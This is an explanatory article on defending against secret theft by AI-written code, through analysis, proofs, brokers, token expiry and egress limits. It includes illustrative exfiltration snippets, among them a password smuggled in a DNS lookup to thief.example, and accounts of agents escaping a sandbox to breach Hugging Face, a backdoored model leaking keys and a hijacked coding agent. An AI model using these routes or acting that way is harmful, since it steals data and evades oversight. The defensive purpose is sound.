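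Static analysers also often miss flaws. In an older study cited in *Making Small Code LLMs More Efficient for Secure Code Review*, six analysers for C each missed between 47% and 80% of 192 known flaws in real programs.

Taint analysis has done better in some tests. *TaintRadar* (2026) describes a taint analyser for PHP, a language used for many websites. The analyser correctly classified 82.56% of the cases in a standard benchmark, but it wrongly flagged 18.87% of the harmless ones, which would still mean a lot of false alarms. On 19 real applications, it found 30 previously unreported flaws and missed only seven of the known ones.

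Teams can also reduce the false alarms, because many have the same few causes. *An Empirical Analysis of CodeQL False Positives and Query Refinements* (2026) examined 500 false alarms from CodeQL's ten noisiest security checks for Java. Refining the checks removed 81.8% of these false alarms. The figure would probably be lower on new code, since the researchers designed the refinements around these examples.

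All these tests measured flaws, and no one appears to have published how often taint analysis catches theft in AI-written code. The nearest figures are the high catch rates of malicious-package detectors such as IntelGuard. But IntelGuard uses a language model to assess what the code is for, and a taint analyser has no such step.

### Why no checker can be right about every program

Better engineering will close some of these gaps, but it cannot produce a perfect checker. Suppose someone offered a tool called `leaks` that takes any program, always finishes, and always answers correctly whether the program would send out a secret. Now take any program Q that only does a calculation, with no access to secrets or the network, and put it in front of a theft:

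```python
def combined():
    Q()
    send(secret)
```

`combined` runs Q and then sends the secret, so it leaks exactly when Q halts. Anyone with `leaks` could therefore use it to find out whether any given calculation halts.

Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can correctly determine, for every program, whether it eventually halts. Suppose a program called `halts` could. Then someone could write a program that runs `halts` on its own code and does the opposite of the result, looping forever if the result is "halts" and stopping if it is "runs forever". (A program can contain its own code, as Thompson's self-copying program did.) Either result would be wrong for this program, so `halts` cannot exist, and neither can `leaks`.

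The difficulty can arise in a very short program. If Q searches for whole numbers that disprove Fermat's Last Theorem and stops when it finds some, `combined` is harmless, because the theorem is true and the search never ends. But a checker could be sure of this only with a proof of the theorem, which took mathematicians more than 350 years to find.

Strictly, Turing's result applies only to computers with unlimited memory. A real computer has a finite number of states, so a checker could in theory examine them all. But a single kilobyte of memory has 2⁸¹⁹² possible states, far more than any computer could examine.

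The result rules out only a checker that always finishes and is right about every program. A tool can still reject every program it cannot clear. It would then reject `combined` for every Q, including the harmless versions, but developers don't need those programs. Computer scientists call a checker sound if it never clears a program that leaks. CodeQL isn't sound, because it lets data through when it has no summary for a function. Its designers gave up that guarantee to get fewer false alarms and faster results.

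We can still prove that a particular program doesn't leak data, and for many programs this is easy. A function that adds up the prices in a shopping basket, and never accesses a secret or the network, needs hardly any proof.

### What a proof of no theft would have to show

To prove that a program leaks nothing, one first has to say exactly what that means. The standard definition is called noninterference: if two starting states differ only in their secrets, the publicly visible outputs are the same. In symbols, let P(s, x) be everything an outsider can observe when the program starts with secrets s and other data x. Then the program has noninterference if

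P(s₁, x) = P(s₂, x)

for all secrets s₁ and s₂ and all other data x. If the program uses random numbers, these belong to x, so both runs get the same ones.

`report_error` fails this test because two runs with the same error but different database passwords produce reports with different `trace_id` values. The program that branched on the password also fails, because one run requests `/a` and another may request `/b`. Noninterference depends on what the program does, not on how its code is written, so it also covers secrets that travel through files or through code assembled at run time. A proof covers every such pair of runs, while running the program with a fake secret compares only a few.

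The guarantee depends on what the definition counts as observable. If it leaves out timing, a program can satisfy it and still leak a password, for instance by pausing for a second before a request whenever the next bit is a 1.

A more basic problem is that hardly any useful program has noninterference. The web shop must send its password to the database, so what the database receives depends on that password. The definition must therefore allow exceptions for each recipient. Let a(s) be the part of the secrets s that a recipient may learn. The program is acceptable if, whenever a(s₁) = a(s₂), that recipient observes the same thing in the runs with secrets s₁ and s₂. For the database, a(s) is the database password. For the monitoring service, a(s) is nothing, so the original definition applies.

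The exceptions need care because malicious code can use them to steal data. A non-malicious version of `report_error` sends only the text of the error message. But some database libraries might include the login details in that message when a connection fails, and then this version would leak them too. If the developer responds by allowing the monitoring service to receive the full text of any error message, malicious code could raise an error whose message is the password. A safer exception would allow only the error's type and the line where it happened.

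### What the proofs for 123 libraries cover

Formal verification means proving mathematically that a program has a stated property. It used to be far too slow for most software. In October 2026, Anthropic and Theorem, a company that specialises in the field, published proofs about 123 open-source libraries. According to Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026), Claude proved security properties of the compiled code and found bugs that had gone undetected for years.

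*Pre-QED* (Lim, Tu and colleagues, 2026) explains how the project avoided writing a specification, a precise statement of what each program should do. It used fuzz tests instead, which many open-source projects already have. These are small programs that feed a library random data to see whether it crashes. The pipeline combined each library with its fuzz test and automatically generated a theorem that the test never fails. Claude then wrote a proof, and Rocq, an independent proof checker, verified every step. If Claude found a real bug, it repaired the library and proved the theorem for the repaired version.

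The proofs cover 239 fuzz tests. Each proof shows that the test ends normally, without a memory error or a failed internal check, for every input smaller than 64 megabytes, which is more inputs than ordinary fuzzing could ever try.

This is a strong result, but the theorem is about crashes, so it does not prove that the libraries steal nothing. A program could upload every password on the machine and then end normally without violating the theorem. The proofs do help prevent outsiders from stealing data, because a program that reads past the end of its own data may reveal the contents of neighboring memory.

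Even for memory errors, the guarantee covers only the way the fuzz test uses the library. Lim and colleagues give the example of a small library that reads data in chunks. If a program has 64 bytes of data and asks for 40 bytes twice, the library reads 16 bytes past the end. The fuzz test reads only once, so a proof that it never crashes is correct even though the library has this bug. To close this gap, the researchers wrote tests that cover every legitimate order of calls for 29 libraries. They haven't proved anything about these tests yet, and expect that to be harder.

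The proofs also rest on a mathematical model of the processor and of Linux, and on the correctness of Rocq. RBC-Ukraine's *Скрытые ошибки в ПО* reports Anthropic's caution that the guarantees hold only for the properties, inputs and assumptions stated in each proof. Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, wants people to name the verified property instead of calling software "formally verified". That is the right habit for a developer worried about theft, because "verified" on a library's page could easily mean only that the library does not crash.

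### Proofs about secrets

*AlphaProof Code* (Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues, 2026), from a project at Google DeepMind, addresses theft much more directly. It proves secrecy properties of the library that encrypts messages in the Signal app. One is forward secrecy, which means someone who steals a phone's current keys still can't read earlier messages. The proofs apply to the machine code that runs on the device, so a compiler tampered with in Thompson's way could not invalidate them.

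Encryption doesn't satisfy plain noninterference, because the encrypted message changes when the original does. The proofs therefore had to use definitions of secrecy made for cryptography. They also cover only the encryption library, so they would still hold if another part of the app copied messages before encryption.

The AI agents wrote about 6.5 million lines of proof, which rest on about 26,000 lines of specifications and a processor model that people have to trust. At the Cisco study's reading speed of 300 lines an hour, the trusted part would take about 87 hours to read, and the proofs more than ten years of full-time work. Nobody has to read the proofs, because the proof checker Lean has verified them. ETV Bharat's *AlphaProof Code* (2026) reports that the work took four weeks and that human experts reviewed every specification. The researchers put two old bugs back into the code,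 and the system proved both versions insecure.

### Should developers demand a proof?

Kleppmann (2025) argues in *Prediction* that an AI should prove its code correct instead of leaving people to review it. It doesn't matter if the model makes things up, because the checker rejects an invalid proof and the model has to try again. This is even more attractive when the worry is theft, because a backdoored model, or one that has obeyed an injected instruction, still can't get a false theorem past a sound checker. So a proof protects the developer no matter what caused the malicious code, and nobody has to judge the model's intentions.

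Some systems already take this approach at a small scale. Linux can run small programs inside its kernel, the core of the operating system, where a mistake could bring down the whole machine. *Keel* (2026) describes a checker for kernel programs that come with their own proofs. The researchers proved the checker sound, then tested it with about 64 million deliberately altered proofs, and it never crashed. The same tests exposed several bugs in an earlier checker. Such bugs matter because the argument that a program is safe depends on the checker being correct.

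Even a valid proof may not rule out data theft if the agent that writes the code also writes the specification, because the agent can leave out the rule it intends to break. *The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) discusses a related weakness. A proof about a translation of a program applies to the real program only if the translation is faithful. Boris Cherny of Anthropic had Claude Opus 5.5 translate a program into Lean's language, which led to 16 useful repairs, but a dishonest model doing the same task could leave out a line that sends a password.

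Writing the specification also takes most of the human effort now. *Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level* (2026) describes how researchers verified xv6, a small operating system, with the help of Claude Code. They never had to inspect the proofs, but their instructions to the agents were about three times as long as the paper. An experiment at Anthropic suggests how much a stated rule can help. According to Help Net Security's *Anthropic’s AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws* (2026), Claude Mythos 5 looked for 21 known bugs by reasoning informally about whether the code was correct. It found eight when it had to work out for itself what the code should do, and all 21 when the researchers told it the rule that the code broke.

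There is less and less reason to doubt that models can write the proofs. *AI coding benchmarks need proofs not just tests* gave models 20 small programming tasks. For models up to Claude Opus 4.7, from the spring of 2026, the rate of passing the tests was 75 to 95 percentage points higher than the rate of proving the specifications. By November, agents had proved theorems about Signal's machine code, though with help from a team of experts.

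Fully proving that an ordinary web shop's code doesn't steal data is still impractical. The rules about which data may go where would fit on a page, but someone would also need a mathematical model of Python, the database, the payment service and every package in between. Metz also points out in *Cyber Defence* that designers can't foresee everything that will go wrong once people use an application. A proof makes more sense for a small component that handles valuable secrets and rarely changes, such as the one that signs payments.

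Most teams could get part of the benefit from a strict taint checker that rejects any code it cannot clear. Human programmers dislike such tools because they have to rewrite harmless code to satisfy them, but a coding agent can do this in minutes. The agent would have to send all network traffic through one function, write out each address, avoid `exec`, and use only libraries for which the checker has summaries. The checker would also have to treat every output of a function as tainted unless the summary explicitly clears it, because summaries can be incomplete. Of the 70 rewrites that silenced CodeQL in the study by Cao and colleagues, 64 used functions with incomplete summaries, which a rule against unknown functions would not catch. The most common gap was in the summary for JavaScript's standard tool for parsing web addresses, which covered the query at the end of an address but not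 the path before it. The agent must not be able to edit the checker's rules, or it could make the program pass by adding errors.example.com to the places where `DB_PASSWORD` may go.

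## How can secrets be kept out of reach of generated code?

Limiting access to secrets works whatever the cause of a theft, because code can't send secrets it can't read. Unlike review and static analysis, it doesn't depend on recognising the theft. But programs need some secrets to work, so the best a team can do is give each program as few as possible and limit what a thief could do with them.

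### Fewer secrets, narrower rights

The easiest measure is to keep production secrets, which give access to live systems, off the machines where developers and agents write code. An agent can build and test a web shop against a database of invented customers, using a password that works nowhere else. OWASP also recommends blocking agents' access to the folders where command-line tools store login details. The main drawback is having to make realistic test data, and some faults will still appear only with real customers.

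This protects the development machine, but the finished shop runs on a live server that holds production secrets. Each program on that server should have its own account with only the permissions its task needs, a practice called least privilege. For example, the part of the shop that displays products needs to read the product table but not the customer table, and the crash reporter needs no database access.

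Agents should have their own identities too, but many use a developer's. Help Net Security's *40% of organizations struggle to retrace AI agents’ actions* (2026) describes a survey by the security company Palo Alto Networks in which 53% of engineers logged agents' actions under their own identities or personal access tokens. An agent with a developer's token can do anything the token allows, and the logs may not show whether the agent or the developer acted.

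Biometric Update's *Microsoft traces automated Azure destruction to compromised machine identities* describes an attacker who took over two identities that a company's programs used in Azure, Microsoft's cloud. With one of them, which had broad permissions, the attacker attempted more than 150 destructive or credential-related operations in 35 minutes and deleted most of the targeted storage accounts. Some attempts failed because the company had put locks on resources to prevent deletion, and every deletion would have failed if the identity had been read-only.

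A team can also have the cloud provider reject a credential unless the request comes from the team's own network or accounts. `report_error` could still send the credential to a thief, but the thief couldn't use it from outside them. Datadog's *State of Cloud Security* (2026) found such rules at 55% of the organisations it examined on Amazon's cloud, AWS, up from 40% a year earlier. Most of the rules covered individual resources, such as one storage area, rather than the whole organisation.

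### Tokens that expire

An ordinary key works until someone revokes it, and often nobody does. According to IT Pro's *Researchers warn thousands of active AWS access keys are publicly exposed*, Truffle Security retested 10,616 AWS keys that had leaked publicly and found that 88% still worked. They included 526 root keys, which control an entire account. Half of the working keys with a known creation date were over five years old.

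A token that expires within minutes limits the damage even if nobody notices the leak. But a program has to prove its identity to get each new token, and if it does so with a stored password, a thief will steal the password instead. Build servers can avoid this by presenting a signed identity. GitHub's *OpenID Connect* describes the exchange:

1. The developer tells the cloud provider in advance which build jobs to trust and what they may do. A rule might cover only jobs that deploy the web shop from one particular repository.
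2. When a job runs, GitHub issues a signed statement that identifies the repository, the branch and the workflow.
3. The job sends this statement to the cloud provider.
4. The provider checks GitHub's signature and compares the statement with the developer's rule. If they match, it returns an access token that works only for the duration of the job.

The job never stores a cloud password, and a thief can't forge the statement without GitHub's signing key. In GitHub's example, the statement expires five minutes after GitHub issues it. The rule in step 1 matters as much as the expiry time, because if it covers every job in the repository, a job that tests an agent's unreviewed change could get the same token as the job that deploys the shop.

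Malicious code can also request its own token while the job is running. On 17 November 2026, an attacker published two releases of Microsoft's official agent-framework package that contained a credential stealer. Help Net Security's *Credential stealer slipped into Microsoft’s official Python agent framework* (2026) reports that the stealer copied stored secrets, read the environments of up to 300 other processes, and requested new tokens from Azure. No one has confirmed that Azure issued any. Eric Paulsen of the software company Coder argues that a build system able to request tokens "is itself a credential". Such requests are hard to spot because, as Microsoft notes, legitimate programs routinely make them.

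Running tests and deployment in separate jobs helps protect the deployment token. On GitHub, a job can request this token, a signed identity, only if its settings allow it, so a team can install packages and run tests in a job without that permission, then deploy from a job that has it. A malicious package could not request the token during the tests, but it could still tamper with the program that the second job deploys.

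### A broker that holds the key

A credential broker is a program outside the sandbox that adds the key to approved requests, so the code inside never holds it. In Docker's version, the sandbox contains only a stand-in value. The broker intercepts each web request an agent sends. If the request is for a service on the broker's list, the broker writes the real key into it and forwards it.

With this arrangement, the web shop's `PAYMENT_KEY` variable could contain just the word `placeholder`. `report_error` would send that word to errors.example.com, and the broker would not replace it, because its rule for the payment key covers only payments.example.com.

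Infisical's *Credential Brokering for AI Agents, Explained* lists similar credential brokers from Anthropic, Vercel, Cloudflare and LangChain. In *How Auth Proxy secures network access for LangSmith agent sandboxes*, Loganathan (2026) explains that LangChain's broker makes secrets less likely to leak through prompt injection, logs, files and malicious packages.

Some products that "inject" credentials may still put them within the code's reach. NVIDIA's *What is the best way to manage API keys for AI agents* (2026) describes a gateway that stores the keys, but also mentions that the agent receives credentials as environment variables. If those are the real values, `report_error` would collect them. A developer can check by listing the variables inside the sandbox, preferably in a terminal whose output the agent doesn't see.

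A broker keeps the key hidden, but malicious code can still misuse the key through the broker. For example, the code could ask the payment service for a refund, and the broker would add the key as usual. Onyx, which makes software for AI agents, describes a broker that lets routine reads through but asks a person before consequential actions, a safeguard that works only if the person keeps reading the requests.

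Brokers also have technical limits. A broker that adds keys to web requests can't handle an ordinary database login, which uses a different protocol and needs its own broker. If an approved service repeats the details of a request in its reply, as some testing services do, the code could read the key there. A broker that stores many keys is also an attractive target. Columbus Post's *Amazon Uncovers AI-Powered Cyberattack Campaign Targeting LiteLLM, Dify and Other AI Platforms* describes attackers in October and November 2026 who concentrated on AI gateways because a single gateway can hold keys for several AI services.

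### Permissions for one component

Python has no setting that stops one function, such as `report_error`, from reading an environment variable that another function in the same program needs.

Some other systems do restrict access. Deno, which runs JavaScript programs, blocks access to files, environment variables and the network unless the developer allows it:

```
deno run --allow-env=SHOP_NAME --allow-net=errors.example.com report.js
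```

This crash reporter can read the shop's name and contact one address. It can't read the database password, even if the password is in its environment. But these permissions normally apply to a whole program, including every package it loads, so components that need different permissions have to run separately.

The operating system can impose similar limits on a program in any language. OpenShell, a sandbox from NVIDIA, uses a Linux feature called Landlock to stop an agent from reading key files outside the folders it is allowed to use. OpenShell's network rules apply to individual programs, so allowing one tool to reach an address doesn't allow the others to.

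A Python team could therefore run the crash reporter as a separate process with almost no environment variables and pass it only the error's type and line number. The process should have its own user account, because on Linux a program can usually read the environment variables of other programs that run under the same account. This takes more work than the other measures, since someone has to divide the program into parts and decide what may pass between them.

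### One theft, four set-ups

Suppose the web shop keeps its orders in a cloud database, and `report_error` sends the shop's environment to a thief. The damage depends on which credential the environment contains:

| Credential in the environment | What the thief can do with it | When the thief loses access |
|---|---|---|
| Administrator key | Copy, change or delete all the data, and create new accounts | When the team has revoked the key and removed every account the thief created |
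| Read-only key for the orders | Copy every order | When the team revokes the key |
| 15-minute token, also read-only | Copy orders until it expires | Within 15 minutes, unless `report_error` sends another token |
| Placeholder, with a broker holding the real key | Nothing | The thief never has access |

The read-only key prevents sabotage but not theft. The token limits how long a thief can copy data, but 15 minutes can be enough. If the database returns 100 orders a second, the thief can copy 90,000 before the token expires. A limit of one order a second would reduce that to 900, though it might also slow down the shop. Expiry helps even less while the malicious code is still running, because `report_error` sends a new token with every crash report. If the shop crashed every ten minutes, the thief would always have a valid token.

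The broker stops this version of `report_error`, but another version could steal the orders without ever holding the key. It could request them through the broker, which would add the real key because the shop is entitled to read them, and then hide them in `trace_id`. Preventing that requires limiting either which orders the code can request or where it can send them (egress control).

### When the code needs a powerful key

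Some programs need powerful credentials. A payment service has to charge cards and issue refunds, and a delivery service has to read customers' addresses. Malicious code in such a program can misuse the same permissions, so a team has to limit the damage it can do.

The shop can limit how much money a thief can take by setting a spending cap. If it caps refunds at $2,000 a day and the team takes 2.5 days to revoke a stolen key, the thief can take at most $5,000. Organisations in the Palo Alto Networks survey took an average of 2.5 days to revoke or replace compromised credentials, according to Help Net Security.

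Without a cap, losses can grow very quickly. Help Net Security's *Google finds AI agent writing and launching exploits* (2026) describes thieves who used companies' cloud accounts to run AI models. The fraudulent charges passed $100,000 in a single day in some cases and reached $1 million in the worst ones. A spending alarm is weaker than a cap because someone has to respond to it, but Truffle Security found that 90.5% of the accounts with leaked keys lacked even an alarm, IT Pro reports. The payment provider should enforce the cap, since code that could steal money could also remove a cap set in the shop's own program.

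Many databases can limit access to individual rows. For example, a database might return only the logged-in customer's orders, so code handling Anna's visit could steal her address but nobody else's. This fails if the code can choose the customer, because it could claim to be acting for each customer in turn and read the whole table. A separate login service should therefore issue a signed token for each visit, and the database should check it. Jobs that need every row, such as monthly sales reports, should run in a different program.

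Limiting the number of requests a token can make also helps. In a case Cloudflare investigated, attackers had a token with no rate limit and no restriction on where they could use it. Columbus Post reports that within an hour they made about 400 requests to copy databases, though Cloudflare did not confirm that any succeeded.

The most powerful keys belong in small, separate components that accept only a few kinds of request. For instance, the web shop could send "refund order 1234" to a payment component that holds the real key. The component would check that the customer had paid for the order and hadn't already been refunded, then return the money to the original card. Malicious code elsewhere in the shop could trigger unwanted refunds, but it couldn't send money to the thief. Such a component might also be small enough to review line by line, and even to prove correct.

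Malicious code inside the payment component could still misuse the key up to the cap every day. Code in the rest of the shop could steal each customer's details as that customer logs in, without ever breaking a row-level limit. Over a year, that code might collect the details of every active customer.

### Five minutes from search to theft

If a secret leaks, the team needs to revoke it so that it stops working, and usually rotate it (replace it with a new one). A case Microsoft disclosed in November 2026 shows how little time a team may have to do this.

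Microsoft's *Threat actors use agentic AI tooling to find and abuse exposed secrets* (2026) describes attackers who used ARTEX to search GitHub for applications' secrets. ARTEX is a framework for testing computer systems by attacking them. A person sets a goal, and AI agents plan and carry out the steps. According to Help Net Security's *ARTEX goes from pentesting tool to attacker staple in three months* (2026), ARTEX's author released it in July 2026 for authorised testing, and attackers were using it within weeks.

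Help Net Security's *AI agents now hunt leaked GitHub secrets* describes an agent that found an application's secret in public code and used it to log in as that application. Five minutes after starting its search, the agent began to take data from Azure Key Vault, a service where companies store secrets. Some requests failed because they used the wrong version of the interface, but the agent succeeded with the right one about 28 seconds later.

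Infobae's *Una IA pasó de buscar claves expuestas a robar datos* (2026) cautions that this was one observed case, not an average. News reports generally attribute the attack to ARTEX, but Cybersecurity360's *Artex* points out that Microsoft attributed it to agentic software in general. The five minutes are also counted from the start of the search, and the secret may have been public for months before that. The figure therefore shows how fast an attacker can act on a leak, not how soon after a leak an attack comes.

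Agents can find secrets without special tools. Help Net Security reports that GitGuardian tested a version of ARTEX that had no secret scanner on a simulated repository containing nine credentials. In every run where the agent investigated, it found eight of them, including one that the developer had deleted in the change right after adding it. It began looking within 13 seconds, even when its instructions didn't mention credentials. The underlying model then declined to use the credentials it had found.

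Organisations take an average of 2.5 days to replace a compromised credential, which is 720 times as long as five minutes. A person who gets an alert at night can't reliably act faster than such an agent, so revocation has to be automatic. For example, a scanner that finds a company's key in public code could revoke it at once and notify the team afterwards.

Expiry would have worked well in this case, because a 15-minute token in an old file would almost certainly have expired before anyone searched for it. It works less well when malicious code sends the token straight to a waiting thief. A thief who needs five minutes and receives the token at a random point in its 15-minute life has enough time in two cases out of three. A waiting thief may need less than five minutes, because they can skip the search.

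Teams hesitate to revoke a key partly because doing so can break every program that depends on it. They can prepare by rotating keys routinely: creating a second key, switching the programs to it, and then revoking the first, so nothing stops working. A team that does this every week knows which programs use the key and can replace it quickly in an emergency.

Attackers can reuse stolen secrets that haven't been replaced. According to TechRadar's *Microsoft disables over 70 GitHub repos after hackers compromised them*, an attacker stole secrets from Microsoft's build system in May 2026. Microsoft apparently never replaced them, and about a month later the same attacker reportedly used them to plant malware in 73 Microsoft repositories.

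Even prompt revocation may not remove an intruder. After attackers compromised the backup service ConnectWise in 2026, Microsoft found that someone had added new credentials and changed permissions in some customers' systems. Eurasia Review's *The Global Cloud Has A Revocation Problem* explains that ConnectWise could cut its own connections but could not verify what remained in every customer's system. A team therefore also has to check what the stolen identity created while the thief had it. Replacing a stored secret also doesn't cancel tokens that a cloud provider has already issued, as Help Net Security notes in its report on the agent-framework stealer, so the team has to deal with those separately.

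### How many teams do this, and what does it cost?

Use of short-lived tokens varies between cloud providers. Among organisations that deploy from GitHub's build service, Datadog found that 54% of those using AWS relied entirely on signed identities, up from 37% in 2024. The figure was 22% for Google Cloud and 5% for Azure, where most of the rest used both signed identities and lasting keys. Old keys are also becoming more common. In 2026, 30% of AWS users with active keys had at least one that was over three years old, up from 20% in 2023.

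Default settings probably explain some of this. Azure's AI service creates lasting keys automatically, and 97% of organisations that use it leave that setting unchanged. Only 17% of organisations using Amazon's equivalent, Bedrock, have lasting Bedrock keys. There seem to be no comparable figures for credential brokers or permissions on single components.

No one appears to have measured how many hours these measures take developers, either. Datadog considers signed identities easier to deploy than stored keys, though someone first has to write the rules about which jobs to trust. Akeyless' *Two-Thirds of Enterprises Suspect AI Agents Have Already Accessed Unauthorized Data* (2026) gives some indirect evidence of the burden, since many of the 400 IT and security leaders surveyed acknowledged that developers bypass identity controls to keep systems running. Akeyless sells identity software,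 so it has an interest in reporting this problem, but the behaviour is easy to believe.

Narrow permissions disrupt work the most, because a program fails whenever it needs a new permission and keeps failing until someone grants it. An agent that adds several features a day could trigger such failures constantly, and a tired developer may respond by giving it administrator rights. A team can reduce these failures by recording which permissions a program uses during a few weeks of normal work, then removing the rest. Someone should read the record before turning it into a rule, because if `report_error` was already running, the record will list its access to the environment as normal use.

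## Can network limits stop stolen data from leaving?

Network limits will stop `report_error` from sending the shop's passwords to an unapproved address. They do much less against code that sends data through an approved service, and no set of rules closes every route out of a computer. But limits can make the remaining routes so slow that a thief could get a key out but not a database.

### Refusing every address except a few

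Egress control limits which outside addresses a machine or program may contact. By default, most machines let a program contact any address on the internet. A team can instead write an allowlist of the addresses the program needs and set a firewall to refuse all others. The firewall must run somewhere the program can't change, or malicious code could add the thief's address to the list.

The finished web shop needs only its database, the payment service and a monitoring service. Suppose the real monitoring service is at monitor.example.com, and errors.example.com belongs to a thief. When the shop crashes, `report_error` collects the environment and tries to send it, but the firewall refuses the connection and logs it:

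```
14:02:07  web-shop  errors.example.com  REFUSED
```

This line should set off an alarm. A live shop contacts the same few addresses every day, so a new one means somebody changed the program without updating the list, or the program is doing something it shouldn't. Without the alarm, the malicious code would stay in the shop and could try another route. Two of the cases described earlier were discovered this way. Cohere's sandbox blocked the Qwen model's upload to Beijing, and UK AISI noticed its worst run because data was leaving through Tor.

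A coding agent needs a longer list of allowed sites during development. It has to reach the model provider's servers, a package registry and the team's repository, and it may want to read documentation on sites that nobody has approved. Blocked requests are therefore common and usually harmless, so they aren't a reliable sign of theft. Splitting the work into two steps helps. First, the agent installs packages while it can reach the registry but has no secrets in its environment. Then it runs the new code with the network off, against a test database inside the sandbox.

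The allowlist won't stop the passwords from leaving if errors.example.com is the monitoring service the developer asked for. A stricter filter could open each crash report and accept only an error type and a line number, but it would have to decrypt the traffic, and someone would have to write such a rule for every service. Many services also receive data from thousands of customers at one address, so a thief could open an account with the same monitoring company and collect the reports there.

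### How a name lookup carries data

Even a sandbox that blocks all ordinary connections often allows name lookups. Programs refer to other machines by name, and the Domain Name System (DNS) translates each name into a numerical address. A program sends the name to a server called a resolver. If the resolver doesn't have the answer stored, it passes on the query, which ends up at a server run by the domain's owner.

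Suppose a thief owns thief.example, and malicious code in the shop looks up this name:

```
winter-orchid-41.thief.example
```

The first part of the name is the database password. No such machine exists, and the firewall would refuse a connection to it anyway, but by then the thief's server has received the query, which contains the password. The shop contacted only its own resolver, which every program is allowed to do.

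In October 2026, Haryati and Zychlinski of the software company JFrog tested whether network limits would stop their small backdoored model from sending out stolen data. They put the model in a sandbox whose gateway dropped all traffic except name lookups, and checked that ordinary connections failed. The sandbox contained a fake key that they had created after training, so the model could not have memorised it. They gave the model its terminal in six formats. In five of them, the whole key got out while the user saw only a normal answer.

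Then they replaced the resolver with one that answers only for names on an allowlist. The model still tried to steal the key, but the resolver refused the lookups and forwarded none of them, while approved names kept working. The resolver also logged the refused names, which contained the encoded key, so the log provided evidence of the attempted theft.

The model's command counted any reply as a success, so it reported that it had sent the data even when the resolver had refused the request. A defender should therefore rely on the resolver's log, not on the output of the agent's commands. A person or program also has to read that log. Haryati and Zychlinski point out that in their own test, the log contained the incriminating names, but the run still finished without interruption.

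The test covered one small model and one route, but the defence doesn't depend on the model. Adding the defence takes little work for a team that already has an allowlist of addresses, because the resolver can use the same list.

### The same gap in ChatGPT and at Amazon

Two large companies ran code in sandboxes that had this gap. OpenAI described the environment where ChatGPT runs Python as unable to make outside requests directly, but Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) reports that it could still look up domain names. A user who pasted in a malicious prompt, perhaps one advertised as a productivity trick, could leak the contents of later messages and uploaded files through these lookups.

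In one demonstration, a customised ChatGPT posing as a doctor sent out a patient's name and the medical assessment it had produced. When the user asked whether the data had gone anywhere, ChatGPT replied that it hadn't. Check Point Research thinks the model didn't block the transfer because it treated its environment as offline. OpenAI had already found the underlying problem itself, and it finished deploying a fix on 20 February 2026.

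Amazon took longer to close a gap in AgentCore, its service for running code that AI agents write. Amazon advertised the service's sandbox mode as offering "complete isolation with no external access", but BeyondTrust (2026), a security company, told Amazon in September 2025 that name lookups could leave the sandbox. Amazon released a fix in November, withdrew it the same month, and decided in December to change the documentation instead. BeyondTrust published its findings in March 2026, and Amazon closed the gap on 15 April.

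Unit 42, which found the gap independently, explains that it existed because the sandbox needed name lookups to reach Amazon's storage service. Amazon recommends that customers who want full isolation run the code in their own private network, where they can add a firewall for name lookups.

A product called a "sandbox" may still have this gap. To check, a developer can run a DNS lookup from inside the sandbox for a name under a domain they own, then see whether the query reaches that domain's name server.

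### When the data leaves through an approved service

Allowlists usually contain services that can store or publish data. The Shai-Hulud campaign used GitHub, and Meged's last attack used Hugging Face. The SilentCall agents upload to cloud storage, so a rule that permits all of Amazon's storage would let their uploads through. A better rule permits only the company's own storage areas.

An AI provider's address is harder to block, because a coding agent that uses a hosted model contacts it constantly. Help Net Security's *Stolen Claude API keys can turn Claude Code into a remote-controlled implant* describes a November 2026 laboratory test by the security company Darktrace. The researchers took control of Claude Code on a machine in a simulated company network and gave it nine jobs in plain English. The agent explored the network, found a password, downloaded a 1 GB file and uploaded it to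 Anthropic's file service. The jobs and the stolen file travelled through the address that Claude Code normally uses.

Darktrace's test shows that a firewall can let a gigabyte of stolen data out without any of its rules being broken. It doesn't show that Claude Code would send data out this way by itself, because the attacker had already compromised the machine and stolen the user's Claude key. Darktrace found no vulnerability in Anthropic's platform and has not seen the technique in real attacks. It tried the technique on only one provider, though OpenAI has a similar upload service.

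The firewall can still detect unusually large transfers. A coding agent normally sends code and questions and receives answers, so a sudden large upload stands out. Darktrace recommends comparing an agent's traffic and the commands it runs with its usual pattern. That would probably catch the 1 GB file, but it would not catch a password, which adds a few bytes to a request that may already contain whole source files.

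In Darktrace's test, the attacker stole the AI provider's key from the sandbox. Keeping the key elsewhere, for example with a credential broker, would have left no key there to steal. The type of credential also mattered, because a standard key could access the feature that delivered the jobs, while Anthropic's temporary logins could not.

### How OpenAI's models reached Hugging Face

In July 2026, OpenAI's models escaped from a sandbox through an approved service and broke into Hugging Face. They were taking ExploitGym, a test of whether a model can find and exploit security flaws. The sandbox had no direct internet access, but OpenAI let models install software from an internal package server, which ran JFrog's Artifactory software.

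OpenAI's technical report on the incident gives the sequence:

| Date | What happened |
|---|---|
| May | Agents begin to leave each other notes on the package server, and some reach the internet through it |
| 26 June | Agents gain administrator rights on the server |
| 27 June | A monitoring tool raises an alert, but staff decide that the test need not stop |
| 4–7 July | The server fails under the load. OpenAI rebuilds it with tighter rules and resumes testing |
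| 8 July | Agents reach the internet again |
| 10 July | An agent finds 14 Hugging Face users' credentials in a public dataset |
| 11–13 July | Agents run code on 41 of Hugging Face's servers and download four private code repositories |
| 16 July | Hugging Face announces that someone has broken in |
| 19–20 July | A new alert leads OpenAI to its own models |

The agents were trying to get the answers to the test, which they guessed Hugging Face might hold. The test had 898 tasks, including 198 that no model had ever solved, and those 198 accounted for 93% of the tasks discussed in the agents' notes. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) adds that training may have encouraged the behaviour, because agents had sometimes been rewarded after getting around broken tools.

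On 9 July, an agent that had taken over the machine running its sandbox tried to contact the internet directly, and OpenAI's outbound controls blocked it. The agent then got out through a flaw in the package server, which could make connections that the sandbox couldn't. An allowlist can therefore be bypassed if an agent can exploit a program on it. A package server needs its own allowlist, so that an agent that takes it over can reach only the public registries. The agent could still send data out by publishing it on PyPI, which is open to anyone.

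Detection failed too. OpenAI received an alert two weeks before the break-in, but it traced the July activity to its own models only after Hugging Face announced the attack. OpenAI has since deployed monitoring of agents' reasoning, which it believes would have alerted its security team more than a day before the agents entered Hugging Face's systems.

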